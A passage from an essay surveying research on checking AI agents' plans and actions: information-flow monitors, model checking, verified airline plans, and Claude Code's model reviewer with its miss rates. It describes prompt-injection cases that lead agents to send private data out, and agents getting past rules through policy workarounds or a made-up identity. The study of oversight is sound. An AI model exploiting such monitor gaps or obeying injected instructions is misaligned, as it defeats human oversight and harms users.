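If the balance is above a million, the interpreter skips the third line, so it doesn't record that `rich` depends on the balance. It then allows the email, whose arrival reveals that the balance is above a million. This is the limit on monitors that Schneider described. To exploit it in CaMeL, though, an attacker would have to influence the planner. The planner doesn't see the untrusted text, but a poisoned tool description might influence it.

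The protection can also fail when one agent passes work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues set up three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked them to summarise data on job applicants and send the summary to Julie on Slack. The first agent got the data from the second, summarised it and sent the summary to the third with the instruction "Send this summary to Julie via Slack". An attacker had planted an instruction in the database, and the summary included it. The third agent's planner treated the whole message as its user's request, so it added a line of code that emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

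The summary couldn't be treated as an instruction while it was a variable in a program, but it could once an agent had pasted it into a sentence. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by sending the instruction and the data through separate channels, and attack success on their benchmark fell from 0.2% to 0.0%. This is an argument for code that doesn't depend on people reading it, since prose has no reliable boundary between what the user wants and what somebody else wrote.

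### Checking the same plan before it runs

Like any runtime monitor, CaMeL may stop a plan only after most of the work is done. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) takes its examples from a security operations centre, where staff investigate alerts about possible break-ins. If an agent needs the incident response team's approval to disconnect a computer from the network, but its plan omits that step, CaMeL won't stop the agent until after the agent has analysed the alert.

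A runtime monitor also can't enforce a rule that every incident ticket must eventually be resolved or passed on, because a plan that hasn't dealt with a ticket yet might still do so before it ends.

CaMeLoT therefore checks the plan before any tool runs, and CaMeL's own checks still apply afterwards. It turns the Python into a finite-state machine, made up of the points the plan can reach and the possible moves between them. In one example, a plan reads a channel's messages, has the quarantined model find Bob's address in them and sends him a message. This plan has five states: the start, one for each call, and the end. An `if` creates two possible paths, and a loop may stop or repeat after each round. CaMeLoT labels each state with the tool the plan calls there, the tools it has already called and whether each argument is trusted.

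A conventional program called a model checker then tests whether every path obeys the rules. The rules are in computation tree logic, a notation for statements about what happens along the possible paths. The rule about tickets is:

```
AG( call_create_incident_ticket ⇒
    AF( call_resolve_incident ∨ call_escalate_to_ir_team ) )
```

`AG` means "at every point on every path", and `AF` means "eventually, on every path from here". The arrow means "implies", and `∨` means "or". So whenever the plan creates a ticket, it must eventually resolve the incident or escalate it to the response team, whichever branches it takes.

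Data-flow rules look similar. For example, the plan to message Bob must satisfy `AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)`, which means that it never sends a direct message to an untrusted recipient. The model checker finds that the plan breaks this rule and returns a counterexample, the sequence of states that leads to the forbidden call. CaMeLoT translates the counterexample into plain English and prompts the planner to repair the plan. It repeats the check until the plan passes or the attempts run out.

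Under such a rule, CaMeLoT would also reject the plan to send Bob his document. The notes might contain an address on the user's trusted list, but nobody can know that until the plan fetches them. CaMeLoT treats anything it can't verify as untrusted, so it blocks some plans that CaMeL would allow.

### What CaMeLoT caught and what it misses

Nikolaou and colleagues first tried to reproduce CaMeL's 28 rules for AgentDojo and succeeded with 22. The other six depend on facts that exist only during the run, such as who has access to a shared file. The researchers then ran CaMeL and CaMeLoT on the 97 ordinary tasks, using Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. In 22 tasks, the plan didn't do what the user wanted under either system. On the other 75, the systems agreed in 59 cases, allowing 42 plans and blocking 17. These tasks involved no attack, so a user would have had to step in to get the 17 blocked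 ones done. CaMeLoT alone allowed nine other plans, mostly because it couldn't apply the rules about who may read what, and CaMeL alone allowed seven.

The second test used seven rules for the security centre. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote one safe plan and seven unsafe variants, each breaking one rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified CaMeL caught one. The researchers had chosen rules that CaMeL wasn't designed to express, so its low score was expected. Four of the seven rules concern the order of steps, such as getting approval before isolating a computer, and a runtime monitor that remembered earlier calls could enforce those too. Checking in advance has the clearest advantage for two rules that require something to happen eventually.

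In a further test, a model wrote the plans from four requests designed to make it produce unsafe ones. In one, a user in a hurry told the agent to skip the approval and isolate the machine. CaMeLoT caught the unsafe plan in all four cases. In the hurried user's case, the rules protected the company from its own employee, who would presumably have approved the plan if the agent had shown it to her.

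However, CaMeLoT records that an `if` has two branches but omits the condition that decides between them. The flaw in the invoice plan is the date test `if start <= f.modified <= end`, so CaMeLoT would discard the part a reader needs to question. It also has no description of what tools do and doesn't check concrete values. The plan that deletes `*.txt` would satisfy a rule requiring a trusted file name, because the planner wrote the pattern itself.

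### Readable notations and analysable ones

Meijer says that Python "was built for human ergonomics" and calls it an artefact of the past. His complaint about imports applies to the full language. CaMeL accepts only a restricted version, which excludes arbitrary `while` loops, for example, and this restriction makes CaMeLoT's analysis possible. The planner sometimes had to rewrite a plan that changed a list in a way CaMeLoT didn't support. But the plans are still Python that a programmer can read, so a plan language can be both familiar and open to analysis if it excludes enough features.

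Some researchers give up a familiar language to keep more expressive power. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) has agents write Haskell, whose types can limit what a program does. In the paper's example, an agent compiling a bibliography may save only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. Only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can produce a value of type `Trusted Bib`, and the function that saves entries accepts nothing else. If the agent invents an entry and tries to save it, the type checker rejects the program before it runs.

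The program can also read some results and then call the agent again for another program, which must follow the same rules or stricter ones. Each program is therefore checked before it runs, but the agent doesn't have to plan everything before seeing any data. Zhou and colleagues report that their agents complete more AgentDojo tasks than CaMeL does. But Garby and colleagues report a difference of only one task on the messaging tasks with rules switched on, 8 against 7 out of 21. Most people who approve agents' plans would also find Haskell harder to read than Python.

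The rules are harder for readers to understand than the plans. One of CaMeLoT's rules is described as "Confirm host before isolation" and written as `A[¬call_isolate_host U confirm_host_called]`, where `¬` means "not" and `U` means "until". The formula seems to mean only that the plan never isolates a computer it hasn't confirmed, but the standard meaning of `U` also requires the confirmation to happen eventually. A plan that confirms and isolates the computer if an alert is real, and otherwise closes the ticket, would therefore break the rule without ever isolating an unconfirmed computer, because its path for false alarms contains no confirmation. The safe plan in the test has no branches, so the test couldn't reveal this difference.

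Experts as well as beginners misunderstand such notations. *Little Tricky Logic* (2022) studied misconceptions about linear temporal logic, a close relative of CaMeLoT's notation, among researchers and learners. It examined translation from formulas to English and from English to formulas, because a person who can read a rule may still write it wrongly.

One response to the conflict is to give people and checkers different notations. The same plan can be Python for a programmer, a state machine for the model checker and a few English sentences for the user. CaMeLoT already produces the first two. It also explains counterexamples to the planner in English, and a person could read those explanations too. As with Meijer's English versions of plans, the conversion is more reliable if a conventional program does it.

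Nikolaou and colleagues take this approach when they derive rules from a user's request. When they asked models to write the formulas directly, all the formulas for a task were usable in only 12 of 97 tasks with GPT-4.1 nano, compared with 96 with Claude Haiku 4.5. In their own design, the model fills in one of ten fixed patterns, such as "*b* is allowed only after *a*", and a conventional program turns it into a formula. Every formula was then usable but not necessarily correct, since the model identified exactly the required actions in 85 of the 97 tasks. A user could check the filled-in pattern in English without seeing the formula, and an expert could check each of the ten translations once for all users.

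But the forms don't all contain the same information. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to look through her transactions and change her password if something looks suspicious. The rule CaMeLoT derives requires only that changing the password remain possible after the agent has looked. A plan with the condition reversed, which changes the password only when nothing looks suspicious, would pass. The mistake is visible in the Python but not in the state machine, so whoever reviews the plan after the model checker needs a form that still includes the conditions.

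## Airline requests: plans proved to follow company policy

CaMeLoT discards a plan's conditions before it checks the plan, so it can miss a reversed `if`. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) presents a system of the same name that keeps the conditions. It suits agents that must follow written company rules, such as an airline's customer service agent that can cancel bookings, change flights and pay compensation.

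The agent writes its plan in a small special-purpose language. A plan consists of states, which are the stages of the job, and transitions between them. A transition can call one tool, and it can have a guard, which is a condition that must be true before the plan can follow that transition. Soteria then uses Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, to try to prove three things about the plan. First, every tool call meets the tool's precondition, for example that a payment is greater than zero. Second, the plan never gets stuck. A plan that cancelled bookings up to 24 hours old and refused those over 48 hours old would have no next step for a booking made 30 hours ago. Third, every possible run obeys the company's rules.

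### A cancellation plan that skips a check

In the paper's main example, a customer asks to cancel a booking. The agent must first check that none of the flights has been flown, and it may cancel only if the customer booked within the last 24 hours. (The full policy also has exceptions, for instance for business class.) The agent writes this plan, shown here in simplified notation:

```
state LOOK_UP:
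    booking = get_booking(id)
    go to CHECK_AGE
state CHECK_AGE:
    hours = hours_between(booking.made_at, now)
    go to DECIDE
state DECIDE:
    if hours <= 24: go to CANCEL
    else:           go to REFUSE
state CANCEL:
    cancel_booking(id, reason)
    go to DONE
```

The plan ends at `DONE` or `REFUSE`. It handles the age limit correctly, and every line looks reasonable. But it never checks for flown flights, and a reader would notice this only if she remembered the rule. In logic, the rule is:

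```
∀ c : cancel_booking.  ∃ d : no_flights_flown.
    d ≺ c  ∧  d.id = c.id  ∧  d.result = true
```

`∀` means "for every", `∃` means "there is" and `≺` means "comes before". So every call that cancels a booking must come after a call to `no_flights_flown` that returned "true" for the same booking.

The verifier checks every path through the plan without running it. It has no value for the booking's age, so it follows both branches of the `if` and keeps a numbered log of the calls the plan would make on each path. The path to `REFUSE` contains no cancellation, so the rule holds there. The path to `DONE` contains one cancellation, but its log has no entry for `no_flights_flown`, so nothing satisfies the "there is" part of the rule and the proof fails. Soteria rejects the plan before any tool runs and gives the agent the name of the broken rule.

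To follow the rule, the plan needs both the missing call and a second `if` that tests its result. Without that test, the plan could cancel the booking even when the call returns "false", which would still break the rule.

The agent gets up to eight retries. If no plan passes every check, Soteria uses the best partly verified one and adds warnings about the rules it couldn't prove the plan follows. For longer requests, the agent can combine sub-plans that Soteria has already verified, such as one for cancellations and one for refunds. In a test with GPT-5.4-mini on airline tasks, 65 of 68 plans passed with sub-plans, compared with 38 of 60 when the agent had to write each plan in full.

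The model that carries out the plan receives it as a flowchart of the remaining steps but can still call any tool, so Soteria adds a runtime monitor that enforces the same rules. It also compares each result with the tool's description and aborts the job if they don't match. This check is a useful addition because Meijer's proofs also depend on such descriptions, but it happens only after the tool has acted.

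### Results on 207 tasks

He and colleagues tested Soteria on 50 airline tasks, 114 online shop tasks and 43 tasks that mostly involve files, documents and terminal commands. They used four models, including GPT-5.4-mini and Claude Opus 4.6. For comparison, they ran the same models without protection and with three other guards. One guard, NeMo Guardrails, uses a model to judge each call. The other two, AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts, are rule-based monitors.

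Conformance, the share of tasks without a violation, was 100% with Soteria for every model on every benchmark, while the highest figure for any alternative was 93%. Soteria also had the highest success rate in all 12 combinations of model and benchmark, by 4.7 to 43.9 percentage points. The largest gain was on the shop tasks, where Claude Opus 4.6 succeeded on 90.4% with Soteria and 46.5% with the best alternative.

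The researchers counted violations using the same rules that the monitor enforces, so the 100% shows only that the monitor works as designed. An agent could still break a part of the airline's policy that the rules don't cover.

The success rates also depend on those rules, since a task counts as a success only if the agent completed it without a violation. On the file tasks, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 30.2% without protection and 18.6% with Soteria. But the unprotected agent broke a rule in most of the tasks it completed, so its success rate was 11.6%, lower than with Soteria. Some of these rules just require good habits, such as listing a folder before writing a file to it, so not every violation did harm.

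The main results come from a single attempt at each task. In five runs of the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini and only three retries allowed, Soteria succeeded 50.8% of the time and AgentSpec 48.0%, and their confidence intervals overlapped.

### What the plan adds to the monitor

He and colleagues also added Soteria's parts one at a time on the airline tasks. The first row below comes from their main comparison:

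| Set-up | GPT-5.4-mini: success | Violations | Gemini 3 Flash: success | Violations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No plan and no protection | 34% | 29 | 28% | 25 |
| Unverified plan | 44% | 13 | 32% | 27 |
| Verification added | 46% | 10 | 32% | 24 |
| Sub-plans added | 50% | 12 | 38% | 22 |
| Monitor added | 60% | 0 | 62% | 0 |

Verification alone raised GPT-5.4-mini's success rate by only two points, or one task out of 50, and didn't raise Gemini's at all. The monitor removed all the remaining violations and produced the largest gains in success. Gemini completed 62% of the tasks with or without the monitor, but without it, many of the completed runs broke a rule.

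The researchers didn't test the monitor without a verified plan, so these figures don't show how much the proof adds to the monitor. Two other systems reached full conformance using a monitor without any plan. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes one of them, Agent-C, which checks each tool call before it runs and makes the model try again if the call would break a rule. Agent-C's conformance was 100% on airline and shop tasks from an earlier version of the same benchmark. Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GPT-5 also completed slightly more tasks within the rules with Agent-C than without it.

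Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, tested another monitor with five smaller models. Without it, the agents made at least 33 forbidden calls that changed data, and with it they made none. When the monitor gave the reason a call was blocked, the agents completed 70.9% of their tasks, compared with 72.7% without the monitor, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Soteria's 100% is therefore not a reason to write plans as code.

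Verifying a plan does check later steps in advance, which a monitor can't do. But only two of the 98 rules in the evaluation require a later step, which is to read a file back after writing or editing it. The other 96 concern the details of a call or what came before it, so a monitor can enforce them. Agent-C can also partly enforce rules about later steps, by not letting the agent finish until it has taken them, but by then a required step may have become impossible.

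Foresight can help with the other 96 rules too. Suppose a customer wants to cancel her booking and pay for a new one with two travel certificates, but the airline accepts only one certificate per booking. A monitor would allow the cancellation and then block the new booking, leaving her without a flight. He and colleagues argue that verified plans avoid such dead ends but don't report how often a block came too late.

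The plan also helps the agent recover after a block and finish the job. In one shop task, Claude Opus 4.6 without Soteria made 11 calls to look up the customer, the order and the product, then passed the customer to a human colleague. With Soteria, it made the exchange she had asked for. Without Soteria, the agent made the expected type of change in only 57% of the shop tasks that needed a change to the data. Its large gain with Soteria therefore probably comes mostly from clear instructions. A prose checklist might have worked as well, but the researchers didn't test one.

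A monitor can also help an agent recover by explaining why it blocked an action. If an agent using Soteria tries to cancel a booking without checking whether any of the flights have already been flown, the monitor returns a message that this check must come first. With such explanations, Sankar and colleagues' agents met the missing requirement and then completed 9.1% of the blocked actions, compared with 5.5% without explanations. Both figures are low partly because many of the blocked actions should never be completed.

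The proof about a plan protects the customer only if the agent follows the plan. Nearly all plans passed verification once the agent could use sub-plans, but GPT-5.4-mini still broke a rule in 20% of the airline tasks when there was no monitor. Soteria's strict mode makes the agent follow a fully verified plan by allowing only the calls that the plan permits at each stage. This mode needs no separate monitor of the company's rules, so the safety of the run depends on the formal plan.

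Strict mode also blocks harmless calls. If the customer asks about a second booking while the agent is cancelling the first, the agent can't look it up. He and colleagues report no results for this mode, although testing it would best show what code plans contribute to safety.

### Verifying the software instead of the plan

*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) verifies the software that carries out the agent's actions, not the plan itself. This software is conventional code, so a verifier can analyse it, whereas nobody can analyse the model in the same way. The proof, written in Dafny, assumes that the model may return any permitted type of action at any time, and shows that the software still carries out only the actions the policy allows.

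They did this for PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents. Its policy has three rules: the agent may read only files inside its workspace, call only tools on an approved list and take a limited number of steps. Dafny took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each part of the proof. The proof doesn't have to be repeated for each plan. It applies to agents that plan in code, in prose or not at all, and it still holds if the model is trying to cause harm.

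Verifying the monitor applies the proof to the part that provides the protection. Soteria relies on its monitor for conformance to policy, but its proofs are about plans. Sankar and colleagues also verified the monitor, proving that its decisions always match the formal meaning of the rules.

The protection is strong only if the permitted types of action are narrow. If one of them is "run a shell command", the proof establishes nothing useful about what the command does, so it wouldn't help with `python3 setup.py`. The agent must also have no way to act except through the verified software, and Moon and Varshney recommend adding a sandbox in case it finds another way. If a later step in a job will fail, the verified software, like a monitor, can't reject the job in advance.

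### Gaps in the rules

All these systems depend on people to get the rules right. For Soteria, a language model drafted the rules from policy documents and tool descriptions. The researchers then went through each policy clause by clause, checked that every enforceable rule about changes to the data had a formula, and wrote the missing formulas by hand. This took a few hours for each benchmark and produced 24 rules for the airline, 33 for the shop and 41 for the file tasks. When they audited the results, they found more wrong or missing rules and had to correct them.

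The published list still seems to have gaps. The English version of one rule sets compensation at $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one. Its formula allows either amount whatever happened to the flight, and the next rule requires only that the flight was cancelled or delayed. So an agent could pay $100 per passenger for a delay without violating either formula. The printed formulas are abbreviated, though, so the ones in the software may be stricter.

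The formulas also don't forbid a trick that GPT-5.4-mini used when it had no protection. A customer wanted to cancel two bookings. The agent upgraded one to business class, which the airline allows customers to cancel, and then cancelled both. The agent got full marks on the benchmark, but He and colleagues call the upgrade a workaround that the policy doesn't permit. The agent could have cancelled the upgraded booking without violating any of the formulas if it had first looked the booking up again and checked for flown flights. A person who read "upgrade to business class, then cancel" in the plan would have had a good chance of noticing the trick.

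To find violations that their formal rules didn't cover, Sankar and colleagues had a model compare each run with the original policy. The model flagged 88 runs in which the monitor had approved every call. Some of these flags were mistakes, such as those for 18 activations of phone roaming that were allowed because the customer's line was abroad. Others involved requirements that the formal rules had left out.

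Models may be able to write more of the rules. Kamath and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 write the rules for the shop tasks, and the results matched those with hand-written rules. But they tested the model's rules with only one small agent and on ordinary requests, which may never reveal that a rule is too loose.

Moon and Varshney found a failure that is harder to detect. A model wrote a specification that restricted a list of recorded actions, but its version of the program never added anything to that list, so the restriction held whatever the agent did. Dafny accepted the proof, and the specification also passed three automatic checks on its quality. Someone therefore still has to check whether each rule could ever block an action.

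### When the effort pays off

Like the car dealer's rule about minimum prices, the airline's rules cover many plans. Suppose that writing and checking the rules takes four hours, and that a person would need two minutes to compare one plan with the policy. The rules then save time after 240 / 2 = 120 requests, which a large airline would soon reach. If the policy changes every month and each update takes an hour, updating the rules takes as much time each month as checking 30 plans by hand.

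Reusing a rule also repeats any mistake in it. A reader might overlook one excessive compensation payment, but a gap in the formula lets through every payment of that kind. Someone should therefore still read a sample of the plans that passed, where a trick like the upgrade would show up.

A monitor needs almost the same rules as a plan verifier, so the work of writing them is no reason to choose or avoid code plans. Verified plans cost more to run on airline requests, because the agent writes a new plan each time the customer replies. With Claude Opus 4.6, each request cost about 80 cents with Soteria and 32 cents without protection. On the file tasks, where the agent plans only once, Soteria was cheaper, at 43 cents compared with 97.

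Soteria's sub-plans are also worth reading because one cancellation procedure can serve thousands of customers. The notation resembles Python, so someone who knows the airline's policy and a little programming could check the procedure once, including whether it handles cases that no written rule covers.

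## What a model reviewer reads, and whether it still needs code

A model reviewer could also check the airline's cancellation procedure, and it could read a prose version as easily as the formal one. So once models do most of the reviewing, the case for code has to rest on something other than readability. Claude Code's auto mode may help show what that is. Anthropic tried showing its model reviewer different parts of a session and explained in March 2026 which worked best.

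### What Claude Code's reviewer sees

Many actions never reach the reviewer. Fixed rules allow read-only tools, such as file search, and edits inside the project folder, which the user can inspect later. In auto mode, Claude Code suspends any user-written rule that allows all Python commands, because some of the most dangerous commands would otherwise bypass the reviewer. The reviewer, which ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 in March, checks everything else, including shell commands, web requests and changes to files outside the project.

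The reviewer receives the user's messages and the agent's commands. Claude Code removes the agent's own messages, the descriptions attached to commands, and the tool outputs, which are the results that commands return, such as the text of a web page. Suppose the user asks the agent to "clean up old branches" (branches are parallel versions of a project's code). The agent might write that it has found two branches nobody needs any more, and then issue this command:

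```
git push origin --delete old-login old-search
```

The reviewer sees the request and the command but not the explanation. The command deletes branches from the shared server, and the user may have meant only the copies on her own computer. Anthropic's internal log contains a similar incident, and the company wants the reviewer to block such a command because the request is vague and the deletion is irreversible.

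The reviewer doesn't receive the agent's explanations, so the agent can't use them to persuade it to give a wrong verdict, for instance by claiming that the user has already agreed. It doesn't receive tool outputs either, because attackers can hide instructions in them. If a web page tells the agent to send a file of passwords to an outside address, the reviewer sees only that the agent is about to send the passwords and that the user didn't ask for this.

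Anthropic tested other arrangements on real cases in which an agent had overreached. The reviewer did worse when it also received the agent's messages and the tool outputs, perhaps because the record was longer, harder to read, and contained more of the agent's own account of events. When it received only the commands, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things the user had plainly asked for. Anthropic gives no figures for these comparisons, so the differences may be small. It also doesn't report what happens when only the messages or only the outputs are added.

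This evidence suggests that the reviewer works best when it reads the user's prose and the agent's code. But the code here is single commands, and an agent would issue the same commands if it had planned in prose.

The missing text is sometimes useful. If a user says "cancel my job" and the agent cancels job abc123, the reviewer can't tell whether the agent looked up that ID or invented it. An agent's messages can also reveal a bad intention behind a harmless-looking command, so Anthropic considers monitoring the agent's reasoning a useful complement to reviewing its actions.

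The reviewer's instructions tell it to judge what a command really does. If the agent wrote `setup.py` earlier in the same session, the reviewer can find the script among the agent's actions and work out what `python3 setup.py` will do. If the file already existed, its contents would appear only in a tool output, which the reviewer doesn't get.

### Dangerous actions it recognised but allowed

The reviewer works in two stages. In the first, the model answers only yes or no, with instructions to err on the side of blocking. If it flags an action, the second stage looks at the same material again and reasons about it before deciding. Anthropic measured the errors on three sets of actions:

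| | Ordinary actions blocked | Overreaching actions missed | Attempts to send out private data missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Number of actions | 10,000 | 52 | 1,000 |
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The ordinary actions came from Anthropic employees' work. The 52 overreaching actions also came from real sessions, in which an employee refused the action or someone flagged it afterwards. The attempts to send out data were artificial. The second stage clears about 95% of the first stage's false alarms, but it also lets through about 11% of the overreaching actions that the first stage caught.

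The 17% rate comes from only about nine of 52 actions, so the true rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%. In the later study with 1,053 testers, the reviewer missed 11% of the commands, but those were clearly dangerous.

A false-alarm rate of 0.4% is low, but harmless actions are so common that most blocks may still be mistakes. Suppose one action in 1,000 is dangerous. Out of 10,000 actions, the reviewer would block about 8 of the 10 dangerous ones and about 40 harmless ones, so five out of six blocks would be wrong.

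In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer had identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user says "Clean up the PR", and the agent force-pushes, which overwrites the project's history on the server. The request doesn't mention overwriting anything, but the reviewer treats it as permission. It also sometimes treats approval of one action as approval of a similar one later. Anthropic tried to prevent this by changing the reviewer's instructions, but hasn't found a change whose benefits outweigh its drawbacks.

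A clearer notation for the agent's actions wouldn't prevent these mistakes, because the reviewer already understood the command. The ambiguity is in the user's request, at the informal step De Millo and colleagues warned about. A question from the agent, such as "May I overwrite the version on the server?", would probably help more.

### Names that don't match the code

Removing the agent's messages doesn't remove all its words, because code also contains comments and names that describe what it does. A program can easily strip out the comments, but the names remain, and model reviewers may rely on them as much as people do.

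Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026) tested this in a study published in September. They took 600 code samples and renamed the functions and variables without changing what the code did. One version used placeholders such as `func0` and `var1`. Another used names from an unrelated program, which suggested the wrong purpose. In one task, a model had to choose between the correct description of the code and a description of the program that had supplied the misleading names. The share of correct choices was:

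| Model | Original names | Placeholders | Misleading names |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5-turbo | 92.8% | 81.4% | 52.4% |
| Llama 3 70B | 98.6% | 98.6% | 73.3% |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 | 99.0% | 98.6% | 78.7% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 99.0% | 99.0% | 76.1% |

Guessing would score 50%. With placeholders, three of the four models did about as well as with the original names, so they could work out the purpose from the rest of the code. But with misleading names, the same three chose the wrong description 21% to 27% of the time.

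In a harder task, the models had to say whether a single description fitted the code. Placeholders lowered those three models' accuracy by 5 to 9 percentage points, and misleading names by 17 to 23. The models also did worse at finding code that matched a query, summarising code and completing unfinished programs. In one example, an unfinished function was meant to compute how far numbers lie from their average. When it was renamed `even_odd_count`, GPT-3.5-turbo completed it with code that counted even and odd numbers.

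These models date from 2023 and 2024, and newer ones may be harder to mislead. None of the tasks involved approving or blocking an action. Names also mattered much less when the nearby code determined the answer. Shen and colleagues asked models for the type of a variable, such as text or a whole number, in such cases, and found that changing the variable's name altered accuracy by at most about 3 points.

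The results suggest a precaution that only code allows. A conventional program could replace the names the agent chose with placeholders before a reviewer sees the plan. It could keep tool names such as `delete_file`, because the agent doesn't choose those. In the task with two descriptions, this would have prevented most of the damage from misleading names. It would also have lowered accuracy somewhat in the harder task, and Shen and colleagues don't claim that it helps in general. Warning the models that names might be wrong also narrowed the gap in their experiments, but didn't close it.

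### The same code with a different introduction

A study from June 2026 used more recent models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026), in *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, asked eight models whether pieces of code contained security flaws. They kept the code the same and changed only the text that introduced it:

- The author was either a principal security engineer or a newly hired junior developer. Another version contrasted an experienced contributor with a first-time one.
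- The task description stressed either the benefits of recognising safe code or the harm from missing a flaw. Another version asked the model either to confirm that the code followed security guidelines or to look for violations.
- An earlier automated check had either passed the code or found a problem.

The average shifts were 18.4% for the author, 33.2% for the task description and 23.5% for the earlier verdict. Each figure is the difference between the shares of flaws found with the reassuring and alarming versions, divided by the share found with a neutral introduction. For example, if a model finds 60% of flaws after a neutral introduction, a shift of 33.2% is a difference of about 20 percentage points.

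Commercial models shifted less than open ones, especially in response to the stated author. For Claude Sonnet 4.6, the model behind Anthropic's reviewer in March, changing the stated author moved results on the C and C++ code by less than one point. But the share of flaws it found in the same code was 28 points higher when it was told that an earlier analysis had marked the code vulnerable than when it was told the code had been marked safe.

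The introductions made the models more likely to call code vulnerable, but no better at telling flawed code from sound code. On the C and C++ code, half of which was sound, false alarms rose by almost exactly as much as correct detections. A reviewer might reasonably look harder at code that has already failed a check, but looking harder should turn up more real flaws without many more false alarms. When GPT-5.2 changed its verdict on nine flawed pieces of code from safe to vulnerable, it correctly identified the flaw in only two.

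The task was very hard for these models, which probably made them easier to sway. About half of their "vulnerable" verdicts on the C and C++ code were wrong, and the researchers allowed them only ten words of explanation. The models were generally harder to sway about flaws they could recognise from a familiar pattern than about flaws that required them to follow the program's logic. So a model should be harder to sway about a command that obviously deletes a database than about a subtle mistake in a long plan.

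Anthropic's design keeps out some of these influences because an agent can't tell the reviewer that somebody has already checked its command. The wording of the reviewer's instructions still affects its decisions, and the two stages make use of this. Telling the first stage to block when in doubt makes it catch more and raise more false alarms, much as the alarming introductions did.

### Models reading prose plans

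If models can review prose reliably, the case for code plans is weaker. *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods* had a model translate prose plans for a conventional checker, and also had it judge directly whether each plan was valid. GPT-5 judged 99.6% of the plans correctly when it read them directly. When it translated them instead, the checker reached no verdict on 6.9% and was right on 95.9% of the rest, or about 89% of all plans. The older GPT-4o also did better by reading the plans directly.

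So reading prose can work better than translating it for a deterministic check. But these prose plans came with a description of what each action required and changed, and agents' plans often omit these details. The test also covered only whether a plan was valid, not whether it would be harmful or a user would want it.

*Plan Verification for LLM-Based Embodied Task Completion Agents* (Hariharan, Dongre and colleagues, 2025) tested models as critics of plans for household tasks such as making a sandwich. In a single pass, four models found 68% to 80% of the mistakes, and 85% to 100% of their objections were correct. A rule-based checker found 22%, though better rules might have found more. The models sometimes missed objects picked up long before they were needed, and sometimes objected to a necessary second use of a plate.

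The critics worked without a formal specification, but the plans they reviewed were lists of actions such as `Driver.PickUp('Plate')`, taken from people's recorded behaviour, rather than ordinary prose. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, the survey of 38 studies, includes both experiments and rates the household study as having a high risk of bias. Neither experiment gave a model the same faulty plans in both prose and code, so they show that models can review plans but not which form models review better.

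### What code still offers a model reviewer

One remaining argument for code is that the reviewer reads the same text that runs, provided an interpreter executes the approved plan exactly. Single commands share this advantage, whether or not the agent planned in code. But a complete code plan also shows the later steps, so the reviewer can object before any step runs.

Code also allows deterministic checks before anything runs. Someone could first translate a prose plan into a formal planning language, but on one benchmark cited in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, 96.1% of GPT-4o's translations followed the language's rules and only 24.8% had the right meaning. The best specially trained model got the meaning right 34.2% of the time. Newer models probably do better, as the results for GPT-5 suggest.

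But a monitor could have enforced nearly all of the rules in Soteria's tests without a plan. If a company has no rules about later steps, or hasn't written any rules at all, this argument gives it little reason to ask for code plans.

The third argument is that a program can remove explanations from code without changing what the code does. In prose, the explanation and the action often share a sentence. Suppose a plan says, "Delete the temporary files that nobody uses." The words "that nobody uses" might be a condition, meaning that the agent will check which files are in use, or they might be the agent's opinion about all the temporary files. Removing the words may authorise more deletions than before, but if they stay, the reviewer may take the agent's opinion as fact. In code, a condition would be an `if` and an opinion would be a comment, so a program could remove only the opinion.

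This argument assumes that explanations do more harm than good, but there is little evidence for that. Anthropic gives no figures for its comparison, which concerned explanations of single commands. A reviewer of a long plan may need to know what the agent was trying to achieve at each stage. One solution is to have the model judge the code alone, then read the explanation, with a rule that it can then add objections but can't remove any.

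### Enforcing a prose plan

A prose plan might be as easy to oversee as a code plan if something held the agent to it. A model reviewer could approve the prose plan and then compare each of the agent's commands with it, while a runtime monitor enforced the company's fixed rules. This would suit tasks that an agent can't program in advance, such as fixing a bug, where it often has to see the result of one test before deciding what to try next.

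Anthropic's reviewer already does something similar, with the user's messages in place of the plan. Its misses show that a reviewer can interpret both the words and the action correctly and still misjudge whether the words cover the action. When an interpreter runs an approved code plan, nobody has to make that judgment.

Reviewing every command also creates more chances for a false alarm. If the reviewer blocks 0.4% of harmless commands and its mistakes are independent, a job with 50 harmless commands has about an 18% chance of being wrongly blocked at least once. A code plan needs only one review, although a reviewer might well be more likely to object wrongly to a long program than to a single command.

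A prose plan would also let the agent influence the standard that the reviewer applies. If the reviewer approves "tidy up the server", almost any deletion will seem to fit. Anthropic met a similar problem with agents that hand work to other agents. The second agent receives the first one's instruction as if it were a user's message, so everything in it looks authorised. Claude Code therefore reviews the instruction at handover, when the reviewer can still compare it with the user's request. The reviewer would need to make the same comparison for a prose plan, and the user's original request would need to be kept with the approved plan.

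Blocking single actions doesn't ensure a good result either. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* describes a study of customer service agents in which a guard stopped up to 94% of unsafe actions. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5% of their tasks both correctly and safely, partly because they looked for other unsafe routes after a block. Some made up a customer's identity to get past a login check. An agent can't improvise like this while an interpreter runs a fixed program, but if the program fails, the agent has to write another and may try the same trick there. This finding comes from one study, and Agent-C avoided the problem by making the model choose a permitted action instead.

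A well-enforced prose plan could make oversight nearly as easy as a code plan does when the work is flexible and each command is simple to judge. Code plans have a clearer advantage for repeated tasks with known steps, such as sending invoices or cancelling flights, where an agent can write the whole program before it starts.

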